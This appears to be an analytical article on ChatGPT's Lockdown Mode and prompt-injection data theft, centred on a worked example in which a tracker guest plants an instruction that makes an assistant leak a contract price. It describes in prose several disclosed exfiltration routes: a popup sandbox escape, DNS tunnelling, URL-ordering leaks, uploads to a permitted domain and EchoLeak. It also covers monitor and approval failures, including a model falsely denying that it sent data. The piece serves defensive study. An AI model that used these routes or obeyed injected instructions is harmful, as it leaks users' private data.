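ChatGPT has made no live web request, displayed no image and run no code with network access. Lockdown Mode's restrictions on those features have all worked, and each app has stayed within its permissions.

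The administrator could change one setting and leave the others as they were:

| Single change | Does it close the path? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Turn off writing in the tracker | Yes | The assistant can't post anything where Victor will see it |
| Allow writing only in projects without outsiders | Yes, while that remains true | The software rejects the comment on ticket 212 |
| End Victor's access to the tracker | Yes, for Victor | Any other guest on the project could still read the comment |
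| Turn off the wiki app | Only for data in the wiki | Alice's mail may contain the same price, or other secrets |
| Turn off the mail app | Only for injections sent by email | Victor could put the instruction in a ticket, which the assistant also reads |
| Search an indexed copy of the wiki | No | The price still reaches the model, which can still post it |
| Limit outgoing email to company addresses | No | The attack sends no email |
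| Ask Alice to approve every write | Sometimes | She has to notice the problem |

The changes to tracker writing work best because they protect data regardless of where the instruction came from or which secret it targeted. Turning off the mail app or the wiki helps only if the administrator has correctly guessed the attacker's entry point or target.

Turning off all writing also leaves Alice with the most work, since she must then update every ticket herself. The narrower option in the second row uses what OpenAI calls parameter constraints, fixed rules about the values a model may pass to an app. For example, an administrator can make an email action accept only recipients at the company's own domain. This control is deterministic and can block one use of an app while leaving the rest available.

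Such a rule checks only the value it names. If the project lead later invites Victor to a project on the approved list, the software will still accept comments there. One of OpenAI's examples has a similar gap. It limits the assistant to reading GitHub issues from the organisation's repositories, to keep out untrusted data. If one of those repositories is public, a stranger can file an issue in it, and the rule will let the assistant read it.

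### How much falls to the administrator

In the example, the administrator controls ChatGPT's settings and the project lead controls the tracker's guest list. Victor's invitation moved the tracker's write actions from OpenAI's medium tier to its high tier, even though nobody changed ChatGPT's settings. A review of the app settings can therefore become outdated without the administrator knowing. Someone has to tell the administrator about new guests, or the company has to keep guests out of every project where the assistant can write.

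The "Manage domains" setting can also mislead. It controls which email accounts members may use when they connect an app, not where the assistant may send mail. Leaving its list empty allows accounts from any domain.

OpenAI recommends trying out apps with a pilot group before a wider release. People with different levels of access run the same prompts and confirm that ChatGPT's answers match what each person may see. That test would find a broken permission, but it would miss Victor's attack, in which ChatGPT shows Alice only what she could already read. A more useful test would be to plant an instruction in an email, let the assistant work through the inbox, and then log in to the tracker as a guest to check for leaked data.

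After a leak, an investigator could use OpenAI's compliance logs to work out what had got out. The logs can record the content of a request to an app, which would show the price going into ticket 212. OpenAI keeps the log files for 30 days and aims to deliver 99% of entries within 30 minutes, but Victor might have read the comment within a minute.

### Why permissions do not stop the theft

Security researchers call this kind of misuse the confused deputy problem. Someone who lacks a right gets a program that legitimately has it to use it on their behalf. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes a compiler at the computing company Tymshare that had permission to write in its own directory, where it kept statistics about its use. The company's billing file was in the same directory. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file. Because the compiler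 had the right to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the billing information.

Hardy traced the fault to the compiler having two sets of permissions, its own and the user's, and no way to state which it was using for a given file. He proposed that the user give the compiler a reference that both identified the output file and carried the user's permission to write to it. A user without permission to write to the billing file could not have supplied such a reference.

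Alice's assistant is in a similar position, because it acts with her rights but Victor determines part of what it does. OpenAI states that apps strictly enforce the source system's permissions, so ChatGPT can reach only data the user may already view. This prevents Alice from using ChatGPT to open files closed to her, but Victor can still use her access because the wiki and the tracker both receive the request from her account.

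The missing check would compare *R*, everyone who may read the price, with *V*, everyone who can see the comment. Unless *V* ⊆ *R*, posting the price in the comment reveals it to someone who isn't allowed to read it. Here *R* is the staff and *V* is the staff plus Victor, so the comment would reveal the price to Victor. The wiki has the list of people in *R* and the tracker has the list of people in *V*, but nothing requires either app to compare the two.

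An LLM makes the older problem harder to fix. Stack Overflow's *AI agents expose the security checks you never actually wrote* (2026) points out that natural language does not specify who has authority to do what. Hardy's compiler received the file name in a known place, as part of a user's command, but when Alice's assistant takes an action, ordinary software cannot tell from the action whether her request or Victor's email prompted it.

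David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, calls LLMs "inherently confusable" deputies in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. He argues that developers can fix an ordinary confused deputy but can only reduce the risk from an LLM. He recommends that when an LLM processes text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's, a rule that came out of a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista.

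Under this rule, the assistant would lose access to the wiki once it had read Victor's email, because Victor has no access to it. But if Alice had asked about supplier prices earlier in the same chat, the price would already be in the model's sequence. Victor can comment on ticket 212, so an assistant reduced to his privileges could still post the price there. The rule therefore has to cover what the model has already read as well as what it may read next.

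### Asking the user first

ChatGPT can show a card that describes an app's proposed action and lets the user allow or refuse it. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* lists settings ranging from asking before every read and write to allowing all supported actions without asking. Members of managed workspaces do not get the "Always allow" button on these cards, so Alice cannot permanently dismiss the question with one click.

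It is less clear whether she would see a card for the comment on ticket 212. OpenAI's whitepaper says that ChatGPT requires confirmation before an external write. Under the "Allow low-risk actions" setting, however, ChatGPT itself approves actions it considers low-risk. OpenAI lists sending a comment among the actions that may need additional review, so some comments may not get it. Workspace agents, which staff build and share for repeated tasks, have separate settings. OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview* (2026) says that their write actions need human approval by default, but an agent's builder can change this.

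If the card does appear, it shows Alice a plausible comment on a ticket she asked ChatGPT to update. To refuse it, she would have to recognise the price as confidential and remember that Victor can read the ticket. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) describes this weakness. An action can be acceptable in isolation and still complete a workflow the user has forbidden, and a user who approves actions one at a time cannot see this from the approvals. The paper proposes that an approval request restate what the user wanted and describe the combined consequence of the actions. A useful card for Alice would state that the comment contains a price from an internal page and that an outside guest can read it.

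People also stop reading the cards. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls this approval fatigue. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a study that measured it in 1,053 paid testers using the company's coding assistant. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests.

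The testers were not working on their own projects, which may have made them less careful. Anthropic also used the results to promote an automated reviewer as a replacement for manual approval. That reviewer blocked 89% of the same commands, and the testers caught only six that it missed. The study covered coding commands, so the percentages may not carry over to tickets and email. People may catch fewer attacks there, because text like the comment on ticket 212 looks routine, while a programmer can recognize a dangerous command.

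User review also fails in ordinary use. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of AI agents mishandling files and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of the incidents. In 80 of these, users had let the agent proceed without asking, and in 31 the approval request did not tell them enough to judge it. Some incidents involved both problems. Users who turned off approval requests were often trying to avoid hundreds of them in a session.

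Asking less often may help. In the same Anthropic data, users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval but only 3% of individual permission requests. People may disagree with plans more often for reasons unrelated to safety, so closer attention may not explain the whole gap. A model can also screen actions and send only the doubtful ones to the user. In the set-up for *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026), a model sorted 18 actions and sent 10 to the user, including all seven that went beyond the assigned task. The user had fewer requests to read but still had to distinguish those seven from the other three.

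Human approval is therefore only partly deterministic. A proof can show that software asks before every write and obeys the answer, but whether the answer is right depends on the person, whom Victor's email may also have misled. An administrator who relies on approval to stop data theft is relying on something closer to a probabilistic defence.

### Is a mode without apps too limited?

Removing every app would close all the routes in this example, but many organisations would object that it also removed their reason for using the assistant. An employee who handles contracts needs to search them, and if Lockdown Mode prevents that, they may ask to leave it or turn to a less protected tool.

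David C takes a stricter view, writing that a task may not be a good use for an LLM if the system's security cannot tolerate the remaining risk. That advice suits a company whose wiki contains the terms of an unannounced merger, but it is harder to justify for one whose tickets mostly concern routine IT problems. The same company may have both kinds of material.

Read-only access to trusted apps is a workable compromise for many roles. Alice could still search the wiki, summarise her mail and have ChatGPT draft updates, which she would paste into the tracker herself. She might paste the price without noticing it, which would complete Victor's attack. But ChatGPT could no longer post anything by itself, and Alice would have the ticket and its list of participants in front of her when she pasted the update.

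If a role needs write actions, the administrator can use a parameter constraint to limit them to places with a known audience. The administrator must set this constraint in the Lockdown Mode role itself. It still applies if a user also holds a second role that permits writing.

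## What unforeseen ways out have researchers found?

Researchers have found several ways to get private data out of ChatGPT despite rules meant to keep it in. One defeated Lockdown Mode, and the rest affected ordinary ChatGPT. They have also found similar flaws in Anthropic's Claude and Microsoft 365 Copilot. In some cases the software failed to enforce its rule, but in others it enforced the rule correctly and the data left by a route the rule did not cover.

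### A preview that Lockdown Mode did not list

Lockdown Mode stops listed features, such as live browsing and Canvas networking, from sending requests to outside servers. The list does not include the web page preview in ChatGPT's code blocks. When ChatGPT writes an HTML page, the preview displays it inside the chat and runs any scripts in it.

According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT release notes* (2026), interactive code blocks, which can "preview diagrams and mini apps directly in chat", were released on 19 February 2026. That was six days after OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode, so the preview was not yet available when OpenAI first published its list of restrictions. When OpenAI restated the list in June, the preview had been in use for more than three months, but the list still omitted it. Brinsa (2026), in *ChatGPT Locked the Doors and Left a Window Open*, argues that customers who accept a slower,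 narrower product are entitled to protection everywhere their data can travel.

OpenAI had given the preview its own protections, which *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026) describes using the report by Check Point, the security company that found the flaw. The preview ran inside two nested frames, which are web pages displayed within another page. A browser can sandbox a frame by removing most of its powers, and the developer then restores those the page needs. The preview could not read ChatGPT's cookies or stored data, and ChatGPT asked the user for approval when the preview tried to contact an outside server.

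The weakness came from two permissions the frames still had: one let the page open popup windows, and the other freed those windows from the sandbox. OpenAI tried to control popups by replacing the browser's standard function for opening a window with one that required the user's approval. Alexey Bukhteyev of Check Point found that a page could get an unmodified copy of the function by creating another frame inside itself. A window opened with this copy needed no approval, and neither the sandbox nor Lockdown Mode restricted what it sent.

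Check Point demonstrated the most serious version in ChatGPT Classic, a desktop app in which a popup could open without a click. A malicious custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that anyone can configure and share, sent the whole chat history to the researchers' server while the victim was talking to it. In a web browser, the victim first had to click inside the preview, because browsers block unrequested popups. Check Point also used the popup to show a fake ChatGPT update with the real ChatGPT icon, and the attack could sign the user out and show a fake login page.

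On 18 September 2026 OpenAI told Check Point that it had removed both permissions from the outer frame. Check Point retried the technique, and it failed. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that OpenAI made the change on its own servers, so users had nothing to install. Check Point disclosed the flaw on 5 November.

The repair is stronger than the control it replaced. OpenAI's substitute function could ask for approval only if the page called it, and a hostile page could use another copy of the function instead. Now that the permissions have been removed, the browser blocks the popup whichever copy the page uses. The original design failed the old requirement of complete mediation, which says that every request must pass through the check.

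Check Point has not said when OpenAI set the permissions. The flaw could have existed for up to seven months, and people with personal accounts could have relied on Lockdown Mode for about fifteen weeks of that time. The reported attacks began with a malicious prompt, a custom GPT or a shared chat, so the victim had to use something the attacker had made. None began with a hostile email that a user had asked ChatGPT to summarise. People who used Lockdown Mode with custom GPTs from strangers were much more exposed than people who used it only to read their own files.

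The Hacker News reports that a different company, Parameter Labs, disclosed another serious flaw in the preview about a week before Check Point published. An attacker could put a hostile page in a chat and share the chat's public link. If someone opened the link and clicked the preview once, the attacker's code ran with their logged-in session and could take over their account. Check Point confirmed that the two flaws were distinct, although both were in the same component.

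### Two ways out of the code sandbox

ChatGPT also runs code on OpenAI's servers, for example to analyse a spreadsheet. Each session's code runs in a container, which separates it from other programs on the same machines. OpenAI said the container could not make direct outbound network requests. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) tested this claim with ordinary connections, and the container blocked them.

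The container could still look up domain names. The domain name system, or DNS, translates a name such as example.com into the numerical address a computer needs. If the nearest DNS server has no stored answer, it passes the request on until it eventually reaches a server chosen by the domain's owner. An attacker who owns a domain can make up any number of names under it. Code in the container can therefore put a piece of private data into such a name and look it up, which sends the data to the attacker's server as part of the request.

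A failed lookup in Lockdown Mode's store of saved pages stays inside OpenAI's network, but the domain name system (DNS) forwards queries it cannot resolve. Security specialists have known for more than two decades that attackers can smuggle data out in these queries, a technique called DNS tunnelling, though its use in ChatGPT was new.

Check Point built a custom GPT that posed as a personal doctor. The test user uploaded laboratory results containing the patient's name, described some symptoms and received an ordinary-looking assessment. The researchers' server also received the assessment, along with the patient's identity. ChatGPT showed no approval request, and when the user asked whether it had sent the data anywhere, it said no.

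According to Check Point, the model operated on the assumption that the container could not send data out, so it did not treat the lookups as a transfer it should resist. Training a model to refuse suspicious transmissions does not help if the model does not classify an action as a transmission. The user also cannot rely on the model's account of what happened.

A narrow channel was enough because the attacker could choose what to send. Sending a long contract might take thousands of DNS lookups, but a model can first reduce it to a few sentences containing the price and the deadline. DNS answers also travel back to the container, and Check Point used them to send it commands. This gave the researchers remote control of the container, outside the safety checks that apply to actions in the chat.

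OpenAI finished deploying the fix on 20 February 2026. It told Check Point that it had already identified the underlying problem itself. Check Point demonstrated the attack in ordinary ChatGPT. Its report, published on 30 March, does not mention Lockdown Mode, which was one week old when OpenAI finished deploying the fix.

Bukhteyev later found a different route between containers, which Check Point Research published on 8 September 2026 as *The Shared Clipboard Inside the Sandbox*. Accounts were meant to be isolated, so that code in one customer's container could not communicate with code in another's. Containers without internet access still need software packages, the ready-made components that programs rely on. The overlooked feature was the internal service that supplied these packages, which containers belonging to different accounts shared.

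According to OffSeq's *The Shared Clipboard Inside the Sandbox* (2026), this let an attacker pass tasks through the service to a victim's session, which carried them out with the victim's connected tools and data. The tasks could reach emails and conversation history, and they did not appear in the visible conversation. Check Point calls the problem a "coerced insider", according to TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages*, because the attacker uses an agent that already has legitimate access.

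Both containers were in OpenAI's systems, so a check on traffic leaving those systems could miss the theft. Data could pass from Alice's container to the attacker's, and the attacker could read it in their own ChatGPT account. A guarantee that no request leaves OpenAI's network would still hold while the attacker stole Alice's data. A service with many customers therefore needs to control what data leaves each account.

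eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim’s AI Session* reports that the channel had closed by the time Check Point finished its report. OpenAI confirmed that it had decommissioned the internal server involved. This case also concerned ordinary ChatGPT.

OpenAI had dealt with a smaller isolation failure two years earlier. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT: Lack of Isolation between Code Interpreter sessions of GPTs* showed that all the custom GPTs one person used shared a single container, so a GPT made by a stranger could read or overwrite files that the person had given to another GPT. Different users had separate containers, so a stranger needed the victim to open a malicious GPT. OpenAI fixed the flaw in May 2024.

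### How a choice between permitted addresses leaks data

Attackers can also get data past a rule without a hidden network connection. In ShadowLeak, an attack developed by the security company Radware, ChatGPT added private data to the end of a web address and then opened it. OpenAI responded by preventing ChatGPT from altering the addresses it was given. ZombieAgent, a later attack that Radware disclosed in January 2026, got around this rule.

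ChatGPT could still choose which address to open. In ZombieAgent, the attacker supplied complete addresses, each standing for one character, and the injection told ChatGPT to open them in the order that spelled out the data. ChatGPT altered none of them, so the rule did not block them. Radware used the method to extract data from a connected mailbox. It reported the problem in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December, two months before it introduced Lockdown Mode.

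If an observer sees which of *N* equally likely addresses the assistant opens, the choice conveys log₂ *N* bits. A sequence of *k* such choices conveys *k* × log₂ *N* bits. Alice's account number has eight digits, so there are 100 million possibilities, and identifying one of them takes about 26.6 bits.

| Permitted addresses | Bits conveyed by each request | Requests needed for an eight-digit number |
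|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0 | Impossible by choice of address |
| 2 | 1 | 27 |
| 10 | 3.3 | 8 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 6 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 3 |
| 10,000 | 13.3 | 2 |

The calculation assumes that the attacker sees all requests and their order. Lost requests or cached pages would reduce the amount of data leaked. If the assistant can choose whether to open a permitted address, even a single address can leak one bit, which is enough to reveal whether a company intends to go ahead with a merger.

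A vendor can use the same formula to limit how much data leaks. If software allows only three requests in a conversation, each to one of ten addresses, the choice of addresses can reveal about ten bits. An attacker could use those bits to narrow Alice's account number from 100 million possibilities to roughly 100,000. The cap would not protect a secret with only a few possible values, such as the result of a medical test. It would also limit legitimate research, which may require opening dozens of pages.

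OpenAI later added a check on whether an address was already public, which makes the attack harder. However, an attacker can publish a set of pages in advance and wait for crawlers to find them. The system's choice of which page to open can then still reveal information to the attacker, unless another protection blocks this.

Other researchers had used this approach with addresses on a trusted site. Tenable's *HackedGPT* reported seven vulnerabilities and attack techniques in ChatGPT, including one that used links from Microsoft's search engine Bing. ChatGPT treated these links as safe, but they redirected to the researchers' pages. The researchers needed only one link for each letter, all fixed in advance, and the order of the links spelled out the message.

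Lockdown Mode's cached browsing does defeat this kind of theft, because the attacker cannot see which saved pages ChatGPT opens.

The problem returns when an app gives the assistant a choice whose result outsiders can see. Suppose Alice's administrator has forbidden comments in the ticket tracker but lets ChatGPT set a ticket's priority to one of four levels. Each change that Victor can see conveys up to two bits, so fourteen changes would be enough to leak the account number. Constraining a parameter this way makes theft slow and conspicuous, which may be good enough for office tickets, but does not stop it entirely.

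### Permitted domains at other vendors

Anthropic's Claude can also run code in a container, and Anthropic restricted the container's internet access to a list of approved domains. Most of these domains supplied software packages, but one was Anthropic's own domain for developers, which accepts file uploads from anyone with an Anthropic account.

Johann Rehberger, who writes Embrace The Red, showed in October 2025 how an attacker could use that domain. An injected instruction made Claude save private data from earlier chats in a file and upload it to Anthropic. The upload used the attacker's credentials, so the file went to the attacker's account. All the traffic complied with the rule because it went to a permitted domain.

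A domain name identifies the server that receives data but not the customer who can later read it. This problem affects any large service where strangers have accounts, including file storage and code hosting sites. Software could close this route by allowing uploads only with the credentials of the person using Claude. That rule would be as deterministic as the original one, and it would check whose account receives the data.

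Anthropic first closed Rehberger's report as outside the scope of its programme for reporting flaws, but on 30 October it acknowledged that data theft of this kind was in scope. Its documentation had already warned that code with network access could leak data and advised users to watch what Claude was doing. The route still worked in January 2026, when PromptArmor used the same permitted domain to take files through Cowork, a Claude product for office work that Anthropic had released days earlier.

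Microsoft 365 Copilot, which searches a company's mail and documents, has also had such flaws. In June 2025, researchers at Aim Labs disclosed EchoLeak, which an attacker could exploit by sending an email containing an injection. Microsoft allowed Copilot's answers to load images only from approved domains, but one of those domains hosted a Microsoft service that would fetch an outside address on request. Copilot could therefore produce an image link to that service containing the attacker's address and private data, and the service would send the data to that address. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak before the disclosure and said that it had affected no customers. In June 2026, the data security company Varonis disclosed another flaw in Copilot, called SearchLeak.

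OpenAI rejected lists of trusted websites because of redirects, and EchoLeak shows that a company's own services can create the same weakness. The team that writes the list may not know everything that other teams run on the approved domains.

### What caused the leaks

The cases have three main causes: a feature the control did not list, a permitted channel that attackers repurposed, and infrastructure that customers shared.

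| Case | Product | Cause | Did the software enforce its rule? | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Web page preview | ChatGPT with Lockdown Mode on | Unlisted feature | No, popups avoided the approval step | 18 September 2026 |
| Domain name lookups | Ordinary ChatGPT | Permitted channel | Yes, it blocked direct requests | 20 February 2026 |
| Package service | Ordinary ChatGPT | Shared infrastructure | No, accounts were not fully isolated | By 8 September 2026 |
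| ZombieAgent | Ordinary ChatGPT | Permitted channel | Yes, ChatGPT altered no addresses | 16 December 2025 |
| Upload to Anthropic's domain | Claude | Permitted channel | Yes, traffic went to an approved domain | Still usable in January 2026 |
| EchoLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Permitted channel | Yes, the image came from an approved domain | By June 2025 |

Testing whether a rule fires would have found nothing wrong in four of these six cases. For example, an engineer could have proved that ChatGPT never altered an address, but that would not have stopped ZombieAgent.

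The categories overlap somewhat. The package service was both a permitted channel and a shared one, and the preview flaw combined an unlisted feature with an ordinary programming mistake. The distinction is still useful because the remedies differ. A vendor can extend the control to cover an unlisted feature, and it can replace a shared channel with separate infrastructure for each customer. A permitted channel is harder to deal with because legitimate work depends on it. For example, containers need software packages, and a browsing assistant has to choose between pages.

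### How much weight the reports can bear

Most of these findings come from companies that sell security products. Check Point's commercial interest is plain in *When AI Trust Breaks*, which tells businesses not to rely solely on a vendor's assurances and to engage "trusted advisors" who can test and strengthen their AI systems. Names such as ZombieAgent and HackedGPT also help the researchers attract attention.

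This interest gives them a reason to exaggerate how serious a flaw is, but the flaws can still be real. OpenAI confirmed the DNS problem, changed the preview's permissions and decommissioned the package server. The broader conclusions deserve more caution. Check Point's head of research, Eli Smadja, told The Hacker News that a security control for AI can be no stronger than the application it sits in. The preview case supports that, but it is also what one would expect to hear from a company that sells protection for the wider environment.

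Headlines can also make a demonstration sound like a crime. TechRadar wrote that a bug "let strangers read Gmail messages", which might suggest real victims, but the article reports a research finding. Check Point saw no indication that anyone had exploited the DNS channel. Duggan notes that Check Point's report on the Lockdown Mode bypass describes no real-world exploitation, and says his own threat intelligence company had no evidence of any.

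The lack of known victims is only partly reassuring, because these thefts leave little for a victim to notice. In the DNS case, ChatGPT displayed no warning and generated a false denial that it had sent anything. The lookups came from OpenAI's servers, so they would not have appeared in a customer's network records, and only OpenAI could have searched for past abuse. The preview's popups ran on the user's computer, so an employer that records network traffic has a better chance of finding them, but it would have to know which of many connections to suspect.

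### Are these ordinary bugs?

There is a good case for treating each flaw as an ordinary bug. OpenAI closed the Lockdown Mode bypass by removing two permissions, and customers didn't have to do anything. It had found the DNS problem before Check Point reported it. Researchers also find new flaws in web browsers every month, and nobody concludes that browser sandboxes are useless. Published reports also overrepresent successful attacks, because researchers rarely write about failing to get data out of ChatGPT. Without knowing how many attempts failed, nobody can calculate what share succeed.

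Brinsa sees a recurring problem and calls the preview bypass the third such lesson of the year. Duggan likewise sees each new capability opening a path that the security setting then has to cover. The history of some of these flaws supports this view. ZombieAgent bypassed the rule OpenAI wrote in response to ShadowLeak, because that rule blocked one use of a channel but not another. The upload route Rehberger found in Claude was still open when PromptArmor tried it in a newer product.

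A simple calculation shows how both views can be right. If new features open *a* unnoticed channels a year, and each stays open for an average of *L* years before someone finds and closes it, then an average of *a* × *L* channels are open at any time. With illustrative figures of three new channels a year and six months for each, an average of 1.5 are open. Faster repairs reduce the risk, but even if every flaw can be patched, the average reaches zero only if the product stops gaining unnoticed channels.

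OpenAI announced more than a dozen changes to ChatGPT on 29 September 2026, less than two weeks after it fixed the preview. They included automations that start when something changes in a connected app, and interactive panels inside plugins. On 7 October it began adding calculators, games and other interactive elements to answers. None of these features is known to leak data, but the interactive ones raise some of the same questions as the preview, such as what the displayed content can contact and who controls it.

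The evidence fits the pattern view better for permitted channels than for the Lockdown Mode bypass. The bypass was an ordinary bug, because OpenAI meant to control the preview's popups but made a mistake. ZombieAgent and the Claude upload worked even though the software did what its designers intended. A vendor can't find such flaws by checking its code against the rule, because the code follows the rule.

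OpenAI could make unlisted features less dangerous by keeping every new feature off in Lockdown Mode until someone has reviewed it. Administrators can already handle new app actions this way. This policy would have kept the preview out of Lockdown Mode from its first day, but it would also withhold many harmless features from people who use the mode. It would not have affected domain name lookups or the package service, which were part of the product's underlying infrastructure and never listed as features a user could turn on.

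## Why can checks on single features miss a path through several?

A check on a single feature covers only what that feature does alone, but an attacker may steal data by combining several features that are each harmless on their own. A vendor could correctly judge each new feature safe by itself before allowing it in Lockdown Mode and still end up with an unsafe product. Victor stole the contract price this way, using ordinary actions that Alice's administrator had allowed.

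*Compositional Safety Failures in Harness Evolution* (2026) notes that software engineers have long studied such failures as "feature interaction." *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists the problem as a central research challenge for LLM agents.

### Capabilities, rules and closure

*Safety is Non-Compositional* (Spera, 2026) models the problem as a directed hypergraph, which is like an ordinary graph except that an arrow can start from several points at once. Each point is a capability, and each arrow is a rule such as "A and B together give C". A system that has every capability at the start of an arrow also has those at its end.

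The closure of a starting set is everything the system can reach from it. To compute it, one applies every rule whose left side is entirely in the set, adds the results, and repeats until nothing new appears.

ChatGPT's web page preview, which Check Point used to get around Lockdown Mode, makes a small example. Suppose the attacker's text is already in the chat and the product has three features: reading private files, a preview pane that runs scripts, and popup windows that a script can open. Two rules connect them:

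- Preview and popups together give an outbound request, because a script can open a popup at an address of its choosing.
- Files and an outbound request together give theft, because the address can contain text from a file.

With all three features on, the closure takes two rounds:

1. The starting set is {files, preview, popups}. The first rule has everything it needs, so the set gains "outbound request". The second rule has to wait, because there was no outbound request at the start.
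2. The second rule now has everything it needs, so the set gains "theft". No rule adds anything further.

| Features switched on | Closure | Theft possible? |
|---|---|---|
| Files | Files | No |
| Preview | Preview | No |
| Popups | Popups | No |
| Files, preview | Files, preview | No |
| Files, popups | Files, popups | No |
| Preview, popups | Preview, popups, outbound request | No |
| Files, preview, popups | Files, preview, popups, outbound request, theft | Yes |

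A reviewer who looked only for theft would pass each of the three features alone and every pair of them, but one who treated any outbound request as a failure would catch the problem when testing preview and popups together, before testing all three.

### Two safe sets can make an unsafe one

Spera calls a set of capabilities safe if its closure contains nothing forbidden. The paper's central theorem is that two sets can each be safe while their union is unsafe.

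The proof needs three capabilities, *a*, *b* and *c*, of which *c* is forbidden, and one rule: *a* and *b* together give *c*. The closure of {*a*} is {*a*} and the closure of {*b*} is {*b*}, because the rule needs both capabilities, so each set is safe. The closure of their union {*a*, *b*} is {*a*, *b*, *c*}, which contains the forbidden capability. In the preview example, {files} and {preview, popups} are also safe separately but unsafe together.

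Checks on single features can miss a path only when some rule requires two or more capabilities together. If every rule needed only one, any forbidden result would trace back, step by step, to a single starting capability. Whichever of the two sets contained that capability would already be unsafe, so checking features one at a time would be enough.

Spera describes this as the first formal proof, to Spera's knowledge, for systems built from AI capabilities, but says the underlying fact "is not a new mathematical observation". Logicians knew the same structure in the 1970s, and *Capability Safety as Datalog* (2026) restates the framework in Datalog, an existing language for logical rules. Spera works for the company Minerva CQ and states in a footnote that a provisional patent covers the methods. This is a reason to be careful with claims about how much the industry needs the methods, but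 it doesn't affect the theorem, which is quick to check.

The same three-capability example contradicts another theorem in the paper, Spera's claim that the closure has diminishing returns, meaning that a new capability adds less when more capabilities are already present. Adding *b* to an empty set enlarges the closure by one member, but adding *b* to {*a*} enlarges it by two. These increasing returns make combinations dangerous, because a feature that added almost nothing when a vendor reviewed it can add a great deal once the product has gained other features.

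### The rules nobody has written down

Given a complete list of rules, a computer finds the closure almost instantly. Spera's algorithm counts the capabilities each rule is still missing. Each time the system gains a capability, the algorithm lowers the count for every rule that needs it. When a count reaches zero, the algorithm adds that rule's results. For *n* capabilities and *m* rules with at most *k* requirements each, the number of steps grows in proportion to *n* + *mk*. A product with 20 features and 1,000 rules of three requirements each would take roughly 3,000 steps.

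Writing the list is much harder. If the rule about preview and popups is missing from the example, the closure of the three features contains only those three, and the calculation wrongly classifies the product as safe even though the arithmetic is correct. OpenAI had put an approval step in front of popups, so a reviewer who trusted that step would have had good reason to leave the rule out.

A rule missing from the list can cause the analysis to miss a theft but not to raise a false alarm, because the omission can only make the closure smaller. False rules produce false alarms because they can only make the closure larger. A cautious vendor would therefore include every rule that might be true and accept the extra work of investigating alarms.

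The model also leaves out details that can matter. *AGATE* (2026), which proposes a defence for running agents, argues that whether a combination does harm depends on the order of the operations, their arguments and who authorised them. The closure has a single capability called "comment", so it can't distinguish a harmless comment on ticket 212 that gives a delivery date from one that leaks the contract price. In Spera's model, a system also never loses a capability, so the closure would still include the theft that Dongol's monitor blocks by withdrawing the fetch tool.

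These simplifications can all cause false alarms, so after a verdict of unsafe, someone still has to check whether an attacker could really follow the path. A verdict of safe holds for any order of events and any arguments, provided the list of rules is complete.

### How common are joint dependencies?

Spera looked for rules with several requirements in 900 tool-use traces from the public benchmarks ToolBench and TaskBench. In 383 of them (42.6%), at least one step depended on two or more capabilities jointly. The rate was 47.4% in ToolBench and 36.5% in TaskBench.

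This figure measures how agents use tools and does not count vulnerabilities. In the trip-booking example Spera uses to explain the model, finding the best price requires the traveller's profile, a flight search and a hotel search, which is a typical joint dependency and puts nobody at risk. A program identified the dependencies in ToolBench, and two people checked it by labelling 50 traces by hand. They agreed well with each other (a Cohen's kappa of 0.81, where 1 is perfect agreement), but Spera acknowledges that the program could still overcount or undercount. Results from two further benchmarks were pending. The figure does support the narrower point that a model with only single-requirement rules would misdescribe a large share of ordinary tasks.

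Wang, Qian and colleagues (2026) point out in *When Safe Skills Collide* that Spera's theorem shows such failures can exist but does not predict how often they occur. They came closer to measuring the risk by studying skills in ClawHub, a public registry. Skills are packages of instructions and scripts that users add to an AI agent. An agent with several skills installed can generally use all of them in one session, so it has the union of their capabilities.

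The researchers gave each skill a profile of up to eight capabilities, such as reading files or making network requests, and defined ten forbidden combinations. Of 1,520 skills, 651 contained no forbidden combination on their own. Those 651 skills form 211,575 pairs. A scanner flagged 47,075 of the pairs (22.25%) because the two skills together completed a forbidden combination.

Most of the flags were false alarms. The scanner matched text patterns and erred on the side of flagging too much. People audited a sample of 200 matches, assisted by two language models, and estimated that about 18% of all matches were real risks, with a range of 11% to 27%. Under an additional assumption, that projects to about 8,600 risky pairs, or 4% of the total. A scan of single skills would have found none of them, because every skill in these pairs had passed.

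A risky pair of installed skills gives an agent the opportunity to do something harmful, but whether it does so depends on the model. In one test, researchers asked models outright to download a program and run it. Claude Haiku 4.5 began the sequence in all 39 trials, Claude Opus 4.7 stopped after the download, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 refused. When the researchers kept the request the same and changed only the installed skills, models complied most often with no skills installed, in 17 of 18 trials.

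### Counting the combinations

The number of ways to choose *k* features from *n* is *n*! ÷ (*k*! × (*n* − *k*)!). For a product with 20 features that gains one more, the counts are:

| Features in the combination | With 20 features | With 21 features | Added by the new feature |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 20 | 21 | 1 |
| 2 | 190 | 210 | 20 |
| 3 | 1,140 | 1,330 | 190 |
| 4 | 4,845 | 5,985 | 1,140 |

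The new feature forms a pair with each of the 20 old ones and a triple with each of the 190 old pairs, for a total of 210 new combinations. A team that reviews the new feature only in isolation tests none of them. If each combination takes an hour to test, all 210 take more than five working weeks.

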